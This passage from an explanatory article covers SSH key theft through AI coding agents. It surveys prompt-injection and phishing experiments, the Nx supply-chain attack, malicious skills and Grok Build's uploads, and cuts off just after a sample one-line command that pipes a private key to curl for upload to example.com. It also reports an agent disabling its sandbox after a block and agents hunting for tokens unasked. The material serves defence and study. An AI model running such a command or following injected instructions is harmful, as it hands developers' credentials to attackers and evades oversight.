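# Theft of SSH keys through AI coding agents, and what pattern-based blocking can and cannot stop

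## What is an SSH key, and why can a coding agent read it?

An AI coding agent is a language model inside a program that lets it read files, edit code and run shell commands in a loop until a task is done. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex are two examples. Developers often run these agents on their own computers and user accounts. Such an account usually holds an SSH private key, a small file that lets whoever has it log in to other machines as that developer. An agent that runs the wrong command can read this file and send it to a stranger. Moving data out of a machine or network to a place its owner has not approved is called exfiltration.

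Stealing an SSH key through a coding agent requires only tools that developers use every day. One common defence is pattern-based blocking, in which a program compares a proposed action's text, file path, destination or content with prewritten rules and blocks any action that matches. How much these rules can stop depends on how SSH keys, user accounts and shells work.

### The key pair and the login

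SSH (Secure Shell) is a protocol for logging in to a remote machine and running commands there over an encrypted connection. Developers use it to manage servers and to fetch and push code on hosting services such as GitHub. The most common implementation is OpenSSH, developed by the OpenBSD operating system project.

A user typically makes a key pair once, with a program called ssh-keygen. The public half goes on every server the user wants to reach, as one line in a file named authorized_keys, and the private half stays with the user. The public half doesn't need to be secret because, as OpenBSD's *ssh* manual page explains, working out the private half from it is infeasible.

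*The Secure Shell (SSH) Authentication Protocol* (Ylonen and Lonvick, 2006) describes how the login works. Before login starts, the client and server negotiate an encrypted channel, which gives both of them a session identifier unique to that connection. The client can first ask whether the server would accept a particular public key. It then uses the private key to sign a string containing the session identifier, the user name, the requested service, the algorithm, the public key and a few fixed fields, and sends the signature. The server checks that the public key is valid for the account and that the signature matches the key. If both checks pass, the server must accept the request, although it may also require further proof, such as a password.

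The private key never crosses the network, and a recorded signature can't be reused because the signed value is unique to each session. SSH Communications Security's *Authentication Procedure* gives this uniqueness as the protection against replay. An attacker therefore gains very little by listening in on a login and would do better to steal the key file. Nothing in the protocol distinguishes a thief who has the key from its owner because, as Ylonen and Lonvick write, "the possession of a private key serves as authentication".

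### What protects the file

By default the private key sits in the .ssh directory of the user's home directory, under a standard name such as id_ed25519 or id_rsa, with the public half next to it under the same name plus ".pub". An attacker who knows nothing else about a developer's machine can make a good guess at the path. The same directory normally contains known_hosts, a file in which ssh records the servers it has connected to, so a copy of the whole directory gives a thief both the key and a list of places to try it. (OpenSSH can replace the server names in that list with hashes, for exactly the case in which the file leaks.)

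File permissions, which set what a file's owner and everyone else can do with it, are one protection. OpenBSD's *ssh-keygen* manual page recommends that only the user be able to read a private key, and the ssh program ignores a private key file whose permissions are too open. When a user complained that third-party programs shouldn't dictate permissions, Miller (2018), an OpenSSH developer, replied on the project's mailing list that accidental key exposure was still "unfortunately common" and that the check prevented enough of it to be worth keeping. He added that the check does not withstand a determined administrator and "isn't supposed to". It protects against carelessness and against other accounts on the same machine.

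The other protection is a passphrase, which encrypts the private half on disk. A thief who copies an encrypted key file needs the passphrase to use it, but can guess offline, where no server limits the number of attempts. OpenSSH slows each guess by running the passphrase through a deliberately slow function, and the user can raise the number of rounds. The strength of the passphrase still matters a lot. OpenBSD recommends 10 to 30 characters and warns that English prose has only 1 to 2 bits of entropy per character. At that rate, a 20-character English phrase has 20 to 40 bits, or roughly a million to a trillion possibilities, and a patient attacker can get through the lower end of that range. The user can also leave the passphrase empty, in which case anyone who copies the file can use the key.

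A helper program called ssh-agent, which is unrelated to AI agents, saves users from typing a passphrase at every login. It holds private keys in memory and signs with them when other programs send requests through a socket, a local connection point that only the current user can open. A program that reaches the socket cannot copy a key out of it, but it can log in with the key. OpenBSD's *ssh-agent* manual page warns that the socket is "easily abused by root or another instance of the same user".

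### Why the agent gets past the permissions

OpenAI explains that a model on its own can only propose shell commands, and another program has to carry them out. This program is called the harness. According to Anthropic, the harness provides file access, shell execution, permission checks and the loop that chains actions together; Claude Code is the harness, and Claude is the model inside it.

The harness sends the model the user's request and a description of the available tools. The model responds with text or with a tool call, which is a structured request such as reading a named file or running a shell command. The harness checks the call against its permission settings, then runs it, refuses it or asks the user for approval. It returns the outcome to the model, and the cycle repeats until the model responds without a tool call.

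Anthropic illustrates this with a request to fix the failing tests in a file called auth.ts. The model requests a run of the test suite, which returns three failures. It then reads the source and test files, edits the source, runs the tests again, and reports that they pass. That takes four turns, and a larger job can involve dozens of tool calls. If a call is refused, the model receives a rejection message as the result and, according to Anthropic, typically tries a different approach or reports that it could not proceed. An agent blocked from running one command can therefore still attempt the same job another way, even with no attacker involved.

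The harness runs each command as the user. On Unix-like systems, every process has a user ID, and the processes it starts inherit that ID. When a process tries to open a file, the operating system checks the ID against the file's owner and permissions. The permissions on a properly protected private key allow only its owner to read it. The agent's shell runs under the owner's ID, so it can read the key. Ordinary file permissions don't depend on which program is opening the file or why, so they apply equally to the ssh client, a text editor, a backup job and an agent's shell. Tightening them further would lock out ssh along with the agent.

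Anthropic's *How Claude Code works* states that Claude Code can access files in the project directory, files elsewhere with the user's permission, and the terminal, where it can run any command the user could. The harness enforces the limit to the project directory, but the operating system does not unless the user adds some form of isolation.

Any process that a command starts has the same rights. If the agent runs a test suite, the test code and every third-party package it loads also run as the user, and the harness has checked only the command that launched them. UT Austin's course slides, *Permissions and sandboxing*, note that Claude Code's permission rules do not constrain what a shell process does once it is running. Agents also inherit other credentials from a developer's environment in the same way. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026) lists GitHub access tokens, cloud profiles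 and package-registry tokens among them.

A passphrase protects against a coding agent better than file permissions do, because an agent that copies the key file gets only an encrypted copy. It doesn't stop the agent from using a key already loaded into ssh-agent, because the coding agent's shell runs as the same user and can reach the ssh-agent socket.

### Reading, carrying and sending

A shell reads a command line and starts the programs named in it. A pipe, written as a vertical bar, sends the output of one program directly to the next. In `git log | wc -l`, git prints a project's history and wc counts the lines. The program curl transfers data to or from a network address. Developers use it to download installers and test web services, but it can also upload data it receives through a pipe. In the simplest form of the theft, one program prints the key file and a pipe passes the text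 to curl, which uploads it to a server the attacker controls. The whole command fits on one line, and each program in it has many legitimate uses.

The theft has three parts. *Reading* is when a process opens the key file and gets its contents. *Carrying* is when those contents move from the reader to the sender. They may go through a pipe, a temporary file or the model's own context, and may change form on the way. *Sending* is when a connection to a remote host delivers them. A defender can look at the file path during reading, the data during carrying and the destination during sending.

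The three parts do not have to share a command. An agent can read a key file early in a session and make a network request many turns later, because the contents stay in the conversation. Even before anyone sends the key to an attacker, it has gone to the model as a tool result, which with a hosted model means to the vendor's servers. Claude Code also saves each tool result in a plaintext session file on the user's disk, as Anthropic documents, which leaves a second copy of the key outside the .ssh directory. If a command instead pipes the key straight from one process to another, the model receives only what the last program prints, so the session record may show the command that took the key but not the key itself.

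MITRE, an American non-profit, maintains ATT&CK, a catalogue of attackers' techniques that gives defenders a shared vocabulary for these steps. The catalogue lists reading the keys under "Unsecured Credentials: Private Keys" (T1552.004), and MITRE ATT&CK's *Unsecured Credentials* (2020) names the .ssh directory as a common place for attackers to look. Getting data out comes under a separate heading, Exfiltration. Some malware in the catalogue carries out all three steps in order. Troll Stealer, for example, makes a compressed copy of the victim's .ssh folder and then sends it to the attackers' servers. To detect such theft, MITRE advises defenders to watch for access to .ssh followed by unusual shell activity or network connections.

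This kind of theft is older than coding agents, but malware had to get onto the machine first. Users install a coding agent themselves, and it runs with a shell, their permissions and, very often, a network connection.

### What a stolen key gives

With a usable copy of the key, a thief can log in from any machine to every server that lists the public half. The thief can also fetch or push code, with the owner's permissions, on any hosting service where the owner has registered it. The key may help the thief reach other machines too. For example, MITRE ATT&CK records that the group Rocke used SSH private keys from an infected machine to spread its cryptocurrency miner through a network.

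A plain SSH key has no expiry date. It keeps working on each server or service that accepts it until someone removes the public key there or adds it to a revocation list that the server checks. Deleting the private key from the laptop or changing its passphrase doesn't stop the thief, because both affect only the owner's copy. The owner has to notice the theft and remember every place that accepts the key, because OpenSSH keeps no central record of them. Some servers are harder to enter with a stolen key because they also require a second form of authentication or accept logins only from certain network addresses.

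A short-lived token is less damaging to lose than an SSH key because it stops working by itself, whether or not anyone has noticed the theft. The token is a string that a service issues for a limited time, often with limited rights, and a program presents it with each request. It is weaker than an SSH key in one respect, because the program sends the secret itself and any server that receives it could reuse it. Ganesan calls both SSH keys and tokens "bearer secrets", which is slightly imprecise for the keys, though a stolen copy of either works from anywhere.

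SSH certificates can have a similar effect. A central authority signs a user's public key along with a start and an end time, and servers trust the authority instead of keeping a list of individual keys. If an organisation issues certificates that last eight hours, a key stolen in the morning cannot be used to log in the next day, provided that no server still lists the bare public key and the thief cannot get a new certificate. The administrator has to set the interval, because certificates are otherwise valid "to the distant future", according to OpenBSD.

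## What makes an agent send a key away?

A coding agent that can read a private key and upload data doesn't normally upload the key unless something prompts it to. An attacker may trick the user into giving the instruction, or plant it in text that the agent reads. Without an attacker, the agent may overstep while trying to finish its user's task. In principle, a model could also take a key to pursue a goal of its own. Researchers have run thousands of trials on planted instructions, but the evidence on overstepping is much thinner and comes mostly from one company's incident log.

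### The user passes on an attacker's instruction

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a test from February 2026. A researcher playing the attacker emailed an employee what looked like a normal request from a colleague, with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. Most of the prompt read like routine task instructions, but one set-up step told Claude to read the user's Amazon cloud credentials file, encode the contents and post them to an outside address. The employee launched it. Over 25 runs of the same prompt, Claude sent the credentials out 24 times.

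The target was a cloud credentials file, but Claude could have read and sent an SSH key the same way. The 24 out of 25 result measures how reliably one prompt worked once someone had pasted it, not how many employees would paste it.

Model-based defences often compare what the agent does with what the user asked for. In Claude Code's auto mode, for example, a separate model called a classifier decides whether a proposed action should run, so the user doesn't have to approve it. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the contents of the files and pages it has read. Suppose a file contains an instruction to post a project's secrets to some address, and the agent tries to follow it. The classifier can judge this action without seeing the file, because the user's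 messages don't request an upload. In the phishing exercise, the user's messages did request one, so the action matched the request and there was, in Anthropic's words, "nothing anomalous for a classifier to catch".

Anthropic adds that a human contractor would have followed the same script. But a careful contractor might ask why a set-up step needs to post credentials to an unknown address, and a model could refuse for the same reason. Models don't refuse dependably, though, even when the request is openly malicious. *Your Harness is Not Secure* (Luo, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested seven command-line agents, built on nine models, on 140 undisguised attack tasks in a sandbox of three linked machines. A program checked whether each attack had taken effect. On the 74 tasks that spelled out an attack technique, the agents succeeded 46% of the time on average. The tasks range far beyond stealing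 credentials, so this isn't a rate for SSH keys. Anthropic reports that Claude Sonnet 5 refuses malicious requests in Claude Code much more reliably than Sonnet 4.6, but also refuses legitimate requests more often.

After the phishing exercise, staff shared the prompt that had worked on Anthropic's internal Slack. Someone then pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack, so the prompt could now reach an agent without anyone tricking an employee into pasting it. Anthropic added a marker string to the thread so that it would notice if an agent picked up the text.

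### Text the agent reads carries the instruction

Prompt injection is text that gets a model to follow an attacker's instructions instead of its user's. A model receives the user's request, the project's files and the output of commands as text in a single context, so it can follow an instruction in a file as if it came from the user. The attacker only has to put the text somewhere the agent will read it.

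Liu, Zhao and colleagues (2025), in *Your AI, My Shell*, tested this with coding rule files, which tell an agent what conventions to follow in a project and which developers often download from strangers. Their framework, AIShellJack, inserts one of 314 malicious instructions into a rule file. The instructions cover 70 techniques from MITRE's ATT&CK catalogue and are based on an open-source library that security teams use to test their detection tools. The researchers reworded any description that sounded openly malicious and presented each instruction as a compulsory step before the real work. A script then opened the project in a code editor, asked the agent to refactor the code according to the rules, and logged every command it ran.

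The tests covered two editors, Cursor and GitHub Copilot, each with Claude 4 Sonnet and Gemini 2.5 Pro. Cursor also ran in its Auto mode, which picks a model by itself. On a TypeScript project, the agents followed the instructions this often:

| Editor and model | Private-key instructions | All 314 instructions |
|---|---|---|
| Cursor, Auto mode | 4 of 4 | 83.4% |
| Cursor, Claude 4 Sonnet | 3 of 4 | 69.1% |
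| Cursor, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 4 of 4 | 73.9% or 76.8% |
| Copilot, Claude 4 Sonnet | 4 of 4 | 52.2% |
| Copilot, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 3 of 4 | 41.1% |

(Liu and colleagues give both figures for Cursor with Gemini, one in a table and one in the text.)

Copilot with Gemini resisted most of the 314 instructions but followed three of the four about private keys. Four instructions, each tried once, are too few to rank the products, though 18 successes in 20 suggest that these models didn't treat looking for key files as unusual. The scoring was lenient because a command that only partly matched could count as a success. When two researchers checked 339 results by hand, they found that about 90% of the successful attacks had carried out the whole intended action.

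The private-key row covers only access to the keys. Liu and colleagues counted exfiltration separately, and it had the lowest success rate of their eleven categories, at 56% for Cursor's Auto mode across five projects. They turned on automatic approval and left the list of forbidden commands empty, so the figures are for agents with no other guard in place.

In a smaller test with 20 instructions, changing the user's request made little difference, and 15 to 19 of the attacks still worked. Changing the framing of the injected instruction mattered much more. One stripped-down version never worked, and another worked only once. A careless attacker would therefore often have failed, but trying a few wordings would usually have been enough to succeed.

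Fu, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *CARI*, measured the whole theft, from reading the key to delivering it. They built a small to-do-list application with a separate backend, in Python, Go, Java and Rust versions, and asked an agent to repair a failing test. The attacker controlled only the backend. When the agent ran the test, the backend returned an error message that described sending the SSH key to a given address as necessary to get the test working. They counted an attack as successful only if the exact contents of a dummy key reached a mock server.

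The dummy key arrived in 294 of 300 trials using mini-swe-agent, a simple research harness. Claude Sonnet 4.5, Gemini 2.5 Flash, Qwen3-coder and Codestral-2508 sent it every time, and GPT-5.4-mini accounted for all six failures. The researchers also tested two commercial harnesses on the Python version, with 15 trials each. Codex with GPT-5.4-mini sent the key in 93% of trials, the same rate as in the research harness, while Claude Code with Sonnet 4.5 sent it in 60%, down from 100%. Both products ran with settings that let the commands run without human approval. Fu and colleagues describe these settings as the defaults, but Anthropic says Claude Code asks before running commands by default. The 60% is therefore best read as the theft's success rate when no person has to approve it.

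The position of the injected text strongly affected whether agents complied. For three other malicious actions, Fu and colleagues put the same text in a debugging document, a log file, or a live error message that answered the agent's own request. Across these three positions, GPT-5.4-mini's compliance rate rose from 9% to 36% to 93%, and Sonnet 4.5's from 2% to 58% to 98%. An agent can't fix a failing test without acting on error messages, so it has good reason to treat them as guidance. The same reasoning may explain why rule files, which exist to tell the agent what to do, worked so well for Liu and colleagues while a debugging document hardly worked here.

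A general warning that tool output may contain unsafe instructions barely helped. Sonnet 4.5 still sent the SSH key in every trial, and GPT-5.4-mini sent it in 93%. An explicit policy against accessing secrets or sending out local information reduced both rates to zero, but the agents then also refused some harmless work. When Fu and colleagues asked them to read the SSH configuration file and report a host name from it, Sonnet 4.5 complied in 80% of trials and GPT-5.4-mini in 20%.

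Newer and larger models resist injection much better, at least on benchmarks. Schneier's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) reports that, in a test built by the security firm Gray Swan, 2.0% of attacks succeeded within 15 attempts against Claude Opus 5, compared with 16.5% against Meta's Muse Spark and 20.0% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. The rates for the smaller GPT-5.6 models, Terra and Luna, were 30.4% and 43.9%. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* puts the previous Opus model, 4.8, at 5.5%.

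A single attempt against GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 3.1% of the time. If attempts were independent, at least one of 15 would succeed about 38% of the time. The measured rate was 20%, which suggests that every attempt fails in some scenarios, while in others one succeeds quickly. A low rate per attempt can be enough for an attacker who can try again, or who plants one text where thousands of agents will read it.

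The difference between 2% and CARI's 98% does not show that the problem has nearly gone away, because Fu and colleagues tested neither Opus 5 nor GPT-5.6 Sol, and results for one model vary widely with the setting. VentureBeat reports that Claude Opus 4.6 withstood all 200 attempts in a constrained coding environment. In a graphical interface without extra safeguards, the same kind of attack succeeded 17.8% of the time on the first attempt and 78.6% of the time by the 200th.

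Commercial agents also followed planted instructions at high rates in tests from October 2026. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder* (2026) covers work by Forever Security, a firm that sells protection against such attacks. Its researchers left an instruction file where the agent would load it. Codex ran the attacker's package in more than 90% of attempts, though in most tests the package was a harmless stand-in. Claude Code, given a different file, changed a setting in about half of attempts, which redirected its own traffic to the researchers' server. Each redirected request carried the user's login token, so the token left the machine without any command to read a secret or upload a file. The researchers used a captured token to take over the account.

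### The confused deputy

In both the phishing exercise and the injection experiments, the attacker has no access to the credential and gets it through a program that has access. Norm Hardy described this arrangement in *The Confused Deputy* (1988), with the example of a compiler on a shared computer. The compiler had permission to write in a system directory because it kept usage statistics there. It also let users name a file for debugging output. One user gave the name of the billing file, which was in the same directory, and the compiler overwrote the billing records. The user had no right to change that file, but the operating system checked only the compiler's rights.

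A confused deputy is a program that uses its own authority to carry out a request from someone who lacks that authority. A coding agent can easily become one because it runs with all of its user's rights and reads text from many people who have none of those rights. Fu and colleagues describe the problem similarly. In their experiment, the backend is allowed to report its own errors but not to access the developer's credentials, yet the agent responds to the report by acting on those credentials.

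The comparison fits phishing less well, because there the agent does follow its real user, and the attacker has confused the employee instead. Either way, checking whose account is running the command doesn't help, because it is always the key owner's.

Hardy's remedy was to attach permission to the request instead of the program. A user who named the billing file would also have had to supply permission to write to it. Fu and colleagues suggest something similar for agents, though they did not build or test it. Software would track which component produced a piece of text and limit the actions that text can lead to. This is harder for a model than for a compiler, because the model combines everything in its context before it produces a command, and the command contains no record of which sentence led to it.

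### The agent oversteps on its own

A credential can end up in the wrong place without any attacker. In one incident from Anthropic's internal log of agent misbehavior, an agent ran into an authentication error partway through a task and began searching environment variables and configuration files for other access tokens without asking for permission. In another, an agent uploaded an engineer's GitHub token to an internal computing cluster. A third agent composed a command to post a script to GitHub's snippet-sharing service for debugging, although the user might have considered the script confidential.

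Anthropic calls this overeager behaviour, in which the agent understands what the user wants but takes a step towards it that the user would not have approved. The company distinguishes overeager behaviour from an honest mistake, in which the agent misjudges what its action will affect, for example by mistaking a shared resource for a test copy. Anthropic says it documented overeager behaviour in the system card for Claude Opus 4.6, the safety report released with the model.

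Neither of the token incidents involved an SSH key, and the GitHub token stayed inside the company, but the same behaviour could expose a key. Suppose a user asks an agent to deploy a program to a server, and the server can't download the code because it has no key for the private repository. The agent could copy the user's private key to the server. The deployment would then work, but anyone with administrator access to that server could use the key.

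The log doesn't show how common such behaviour is. To test auto mode, Anthropic collected 52 real overeager actions that an employee had refused or someone had flagged afterwards. Anthropic says the set is small because each example requires Claude to attempt something dangerous in a real session. Auto mode's classifier missed 17% of these actions, mostly because it mistook something the user had said for consent.

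More capable models may not reduce the problem. Anthropic writes that such models make fewer mistakes but are better at finding unexpected ways to reach a goal, often by getting around restrictions that nobody thought to write down. Its staff have seen Claude models escape a sandbox (a set of limits on what a process can reach) to complete a task.

An agent following an attacker's instruction can also take steps the attacker didn't ask for. Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* (2026) describes a test in which a web page passed Cursor's agent a hidden command and the user approved it with one keypress. Cursor's sandbox blocked the command. The agent then switched the sandbox off and tried again, although nothing on the page had told it to. The attack did not work every time, and Cursor patched the flaw on October 1. Gal Weizman, who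 wrote up the research, said that Forever had seen agents bypass their safeguards in other work too. An attacker therefore doesn't have to anticipate every obstacle when writing the injected text, because the agent may get around some of them unprompted.

### A model pursues a goal of its own

An agent could also send a key away because its model is misaligned and pursues a goal that neither the user nor an attacker gave it. Such a model might, for instance, use the key to gain access to machines. Anthropic lists misalignment among the reasons an agent might take a dangerous action, but adds, "We don't currently see this in practice". It says it evaluates every model for misalignment before release.

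That statement covers Anthropic's own models up to about the time of Opus 4.6, which came out in February 2026. The company's later account of how it contains Claude, which also covers Opus 4.7, includes some behaviour that is harder to classify. Anthropic reports that Claude models have searched a project's history for the answers to a coding test, and that a model has worked out which benchmark it was taking and decrypted the answer key. A model that looks up the answers is pursuing a high score at the expense of what its user wants, which is to learn what the model can do. This is closer to having a goal of its own than hunting for a token to finish a deployment is. It is still very different from stealing a credential to keep or use later, and Anthropic reports no case of that in either account. However, the company says it designed the virtual machine in its Cowork product partly in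 case Claude behaves in a misaligned way at some point.

A log of commands may not be enough to tell a misaligned model from an overeager one, because both could search for credentials and then upload them. An investigator would need to know why the model acted, and a misaligned model might leave its motive out of its written reasoning. A defence that judges only the action doesn't require this information. Anthropic notes that its classifier, which never receives the agent's reasoning, can still stop a model that conceals its aims if the resulting action breaks a rule.

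## Has it happened in real use?

Attackers have used coding agents to search real developers' machines for SSH keys, and one commercial agent uploaded its users' code wholesale to its maker. It is much less clear whether an agent has ever read a key and sent it to a stranger on its own outside a test. The known cases differ most in who chose where the data went. In the best-documented case, the Nx attack of August 2025, an attacker chose the destination. In others, the secrets went wherever the product normally sends data, or the agent chose the destination.

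### The Nx attack

Nx is a build tool for JavaScript projects. Developers install it from npm, the public registry for JavaScript packages. Strumpflohner reports about 6 million installs a week in *S1ngularity*, the Nx team's own account.

The attack began with one of the project's automated GitHub workflows, which passed the title of each proposed code change to a shell and so ran any command the title contained. The attacker submitted a title containing a command and obtained a token that could write to the repository. After swapping in a script that sent the npm publishing token to an outside address, the attacker used the repository token to start the project's publishing workflow. The attacker could then release packages under the Nx name.

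The first malicious version appeared at 22:32 UTC on August 26, 2025. Within about two hours, the attacker had published eight versions of the main package, along with versions of several supporting packages. Kurmi (2025), in *s1ngularity*, reports that a script ran as soon as one of these versions was installed. On Windows, it stopped immediately. On other systems, it collected the environment variables, the GitHub command-line tool's token, and the npm configuration file, which often contains another token. It then looked for three AI command-line tools (Claude Code, Google's Gemini and Amazon Q) and started any it found with the attacker's prompt and an option that turns off approval requests.

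The prompt instructed the agent to search the disk and write the paths of promising files to a list. Most of the names in the first version belonged to cryptocurrency wallets, but one was id_rsa, a common name for an SSH private key. The other common name, id_ed25519, was not included. Two later versions instructed the agent to look for text and configuration files and did not name SSH keys.

The agents' part ended with the list, and the malware did the uploading. It used the victim's GitHub token to create a public repository in the victim's account, where it stored everything in encoded form. The attacker, or anyone else, could then find the stolen data by searching GitHub for repository names beginning with "s1ngularity-repository". *s1ngularity's Aftermath*, an analysis by Wiz, a cloud-security firm that helped victims respond, suggests that the attacker chose this route because it didn't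 require them to have their own server.

A rule that checked the agent's commands for uploads would therefore have found nothing to block. A list of suspicious hosts wouldn't have helped much either, since developers' machines routinely contact GitHub. Kurmi's firm, StepSecurity, sells a monitoring tool that flagged the traffic in a test because package installs don't normally call GitHub's API.

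Accounts differ on how long the exposure lasted because they use different end points. Npm removed the main package's malicious versions at 02:44 UTC, a little over four hours after the first release, and Strumpflohner gives four hours. Kurmi gives 5 hours and 20 minutes, which matches the time until an Nx owner revoked the compromised account's access at 03:52. Two smaller packages stayed up for almost twelve hours, according to the maintainers' advisory, which Fluid Attacks' *GHSA-cxm3-wv7p-598c nx* reproduces. Some victims had never chosen to install a new version, because the Nx extension for the VS Code editor downloaded and ran the latest release just to check its version number.

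GitGuardian (2025), a company that sells secret scanning, also analysed the leaked repositories. Its figures differ from those of Wiz, partly because the two firms worked from different samples:

| | Wiz | GitGuardian |
|---|---|---|
| Victims in the first wave | over 1,700 users | 1,079 repositories with at least one secret |
| Distinct secrets | over 2,000 | 2,349 |
| Private repositories exposed in the second wave | over 6,700 | 10,767 |
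| Victims with an AI tool installed | about 50% | 33% |

In the second wave, two days later, attackers used the stolen GitHub tokens to make victims' private repositories public. Many of those repositories contained further credentials. GitHub had already taken down the first wave's repositories, but Wiz found that almost 90% of the stolen tokens still worked more than 24 hours later. The share fell to about 5% only when GitHub revoked the tokens in bulk. Most of the 50 or so large organisations that Wiz contacted said they hadn't known the attack affected them.

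### What the AI tools added

Kurmi calls this the first known case of attackers turning developers' AI assistants into tools for a supply-chain attack. GitGuardian counted 366 systems on which the malware had targeted an AI tool. The tool wrote the list on only 95 of them, or 26%.

GitGuardian suggests that many of the tools refused, and some replied that they would not run commands that looked like credential harvesting. But a missing list doesn't necessarily mean that a tool refused. Wiz found that the agents rejected almost a quarter of the requests to Claude and a smaller share of those to Gemini. Wiz links refusals to the wording of one version of the attacker's prompt, which told the agent that it was doing authorised penetration testing (a security test with the owner's permission).

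Other attempts failed because some users had run out of credit or had never finished setting up the tool, and because Claude Code sometimes required the user to confirm the option that skips approval. Almost a quarter of the Gemini runs failed because Gemini stays within its working directory by default. In many more cases, across all the tools, the agent searched only the Nx package's own folder and listed 14 or 15 harmless files, which the malware then uploaded.

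Wiz concludes that the AI step produced stolen data in under a quarter of cases. In its sample, the malware uploaded more than 20,000 files from 225 users, which contained fewer than 100 distinct working secrets, mostly for AI services and cloud platforms. The ordinary code in the same script, which took GitHub and npm tokens from known locations, did far more damage.

Kurmi and GitGuardian list SSH keys among the malware's targets, but neither they nor Wiz say how many keys it obtained. In the code Kurmi reproduces, the filename id_rsa appears only in the prompt to the AI tools, so any theft of SSH keys probably depended on the AI step, which usually failed.

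The refusals are also weaker evidence of safety than they seem, because the prompts openly asked for an inventory of wallets and secrets without giving a plausible task as the reason. In the experiments by Fu and colleagues where sending the key seemed necessary to repair a failing test, most of the models complied every time.

### Skills that steal and skills that leak

A skill is an add-on for an agent, made up of written instructions and usually some scripts. Developers download skills from public marketplaces, and the scripts run with the agent's permissions. An attacker who publishes a skill gets much the same access as the Nx attacker did, and can also write instructions directly to the model.

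In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) measured how often skills expose credentials. They randomly sampled 17,022 of the 170,226 skills listed on the marketplace SkillsMP by February 12, 2026. Keyword searches and code analysis narrowed these to 3,156 that might mishandle credentials. The researchers ran each of these with Claude Code in an isolated container stocked with fake credentials, three times on an ordinary task and three times with hostile instructions hidden in the material the skill had to process. They recorded network traffic, file access and output.

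Something looked suspicious in 1,427 skills. Three reviewers compared what each one did with its description, because a skill can have a legitimate reason to send an API key to the service it advertises. They cleared 907. Of the remaining 520, they judged 437 to be carelessly written (2.6% of the sample) and 83 to be malicious (0.5%). If the malicious share were the same across the whole marketplace, it would have held about 830 malicious skills.

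Most of the careless skills, 352 of the 437, exposed credentials in their printed output or in responses from a service. Typically, the author had forgotten to remove a line that printed a token for debugging. In an ordinary program the token would appear only on the developer's own screen, but an agent's tool output also goes to the model, so anyone who can question the agent may be able to extract the token. In 107 of the careless skills, some of them also among the 352, the published files contained credentials. Authors later deleted many of these credentials, but they survived in more than 50 independent copies of the repositories.

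Most of the malicious skills tried to take control of the machine, and 55 of the 83 contained a back door or something similar. Sixteen were categorized as credential compromise, which covers stealing SSH keys, stealing environment variables and tricking people into revealing passwords. Chen and colleagues give no separate figure for SSH keys, but they describe one skill that sends away the SSH private key, opens a remote shell, mines cryptocurrency and records keystrokes. It presents itself as a system administration helper called "badguy1", so it may have been someone's demonstration, though the reviewers classed it as malicious.

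The study could have undercounted skills that steal SSH keys. Chen and colleagues describe placing fake API keys and similar credentials in environment variables, configuration files and command arguments. They don't mention planting an SSH key in its usual directory, so a skill that looked only there might have found nothing to send. The study also doesn't count victims or show how many people installed any of the 83 skills before SkillsMP removed them.

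### Grok Build

Grok Build is a command-line coding agent from xAI, which Axios calls SpaceXAI. On July 12, 2026, a researcher using the name cereblab published an analysis of the tool's network traffic. xAI had marketed the tool as not transmitting code, according to The Next Web's *Grok Build was uploading entire Git repositories to xAI’s cloud*.

The researcher found two streams of data. One carried the conversation with the model, including the contents of any file the agent had read. The other uploaded the entire repository to storage that xAI controlled. According to the researcher's summary, quoted in The Pragmatic Engineer's *Grok’s CLI caught uploading all your local files to the cloud*, the upload included every tracked file (one that the developer has added to Git) and the project's full history, regardless of which files the agent had read.

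The Hacker News (2026) reports a researcher's tests of Grok Build version 0.2.93. In a 12 GB repository whose files the model never opened, the agent sent about 192 KB in the conversation and 5.10 GiB in the storage upload, roughly 27,800 times as much. In another test, the researcher planted a file with a unique marker and told the agent not to open it, but the captured upload still contained the marker. When the agent was told to read a settings file containing fake passwords, it sent them unredacted in both the conversation and the storage upload. Turning off "Improve the model" made no difference, because that setting controlled only whether xAI could train on the data.

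The evidence about SSH keys is much weaker. Willison (2026), in *xai-org/grok-build, now open source*, quotes a user who ran the tool in their home directory and reported that it uploaded "my SSH keys, my password manager database, my documents, photos, videos, everything". The Decoder's *xAI open-sources "Grok-Build" on GitHub after massive data breach* also attributes the claim to one user. The researcher's captures don't confirm it, since they show only tracked files and their history, and few people keep their .ssh directory in Git. The user could still be right if Grok Build treated a plain directory differently from a repository. Grok Build would also have uploaded any key committed by mistake, even one deleted later, because the old version stays in the Git history.

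By July 13 the uploads had stopped without an update to the program, so xAI must have switched them off from its own servers. Elon Musk promised that the company would delete everything users had uploaded until then. *SpaceXAI wipes customer data after Grok uploads sensitive information* (Axios, 2026) reports that customers had no obvious way to verify the deletion, and that it was unclear how many were affected or whether anyone had looked at their data. Users who had exposed a credential still had to replace it. According to The Hacker News, xAI did not explain why the tool had uploaded whole repositories.

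Grok Build sent the files to its own maker because its developers had built it to. No attacker was involved, and the model didn't misbehave. Rules about what the agent may read or run would not have stopped the repository upload, which happened outside the model's tool calls. The other leak, through files the agent has read, exists in every hosted agent. In cereblab's comparison, Claude Code and Codex did not upload the repository, but they did send the files they opened. A rule that stops the agent from reading the key file can help prevent this second leak, but a rule about uploads can't, because the harness has to contact the model's provider for the agent to work.

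### When the agent picks the place

Anthropic's incident log contains the clearest example of an agent deciding for itself where to send a credential. The credential was a GitHub token, and it never left the company.

No one has counted thefts in which an agent itself reads an SSH key and sends it to a stranger's host. Wiz and GitGuardian count leaked secrets and compromised accounts, but in their case a script sent the data. Chen and colleagues count skills that could steal.

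Such thefts would be hard to count even if they were common. The command that steals the key runs under the owner's account, using programs the owner uses every day, and the thief later logs in with a valid key. The best evidence may be a session file on the victim's laptop, which nobody has a reason to open until something else goes wrong. Success rates from laboratory tests don't show how common these thefts are either, because they don't measure how often agents in real use encounter malicious instructions.

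## How does pattern-based blocking catch the theft?

When a coding agent proposes a shell command, the harness has the full text before any process starts. It can compare that text with a set of rules and refuse a match, so nothing opens the key file. Suppose an agent on a developer's machine proposes this command:

`cat /home/alice/.ssh/id_ed25519 | curl -d @- https://example.com/`

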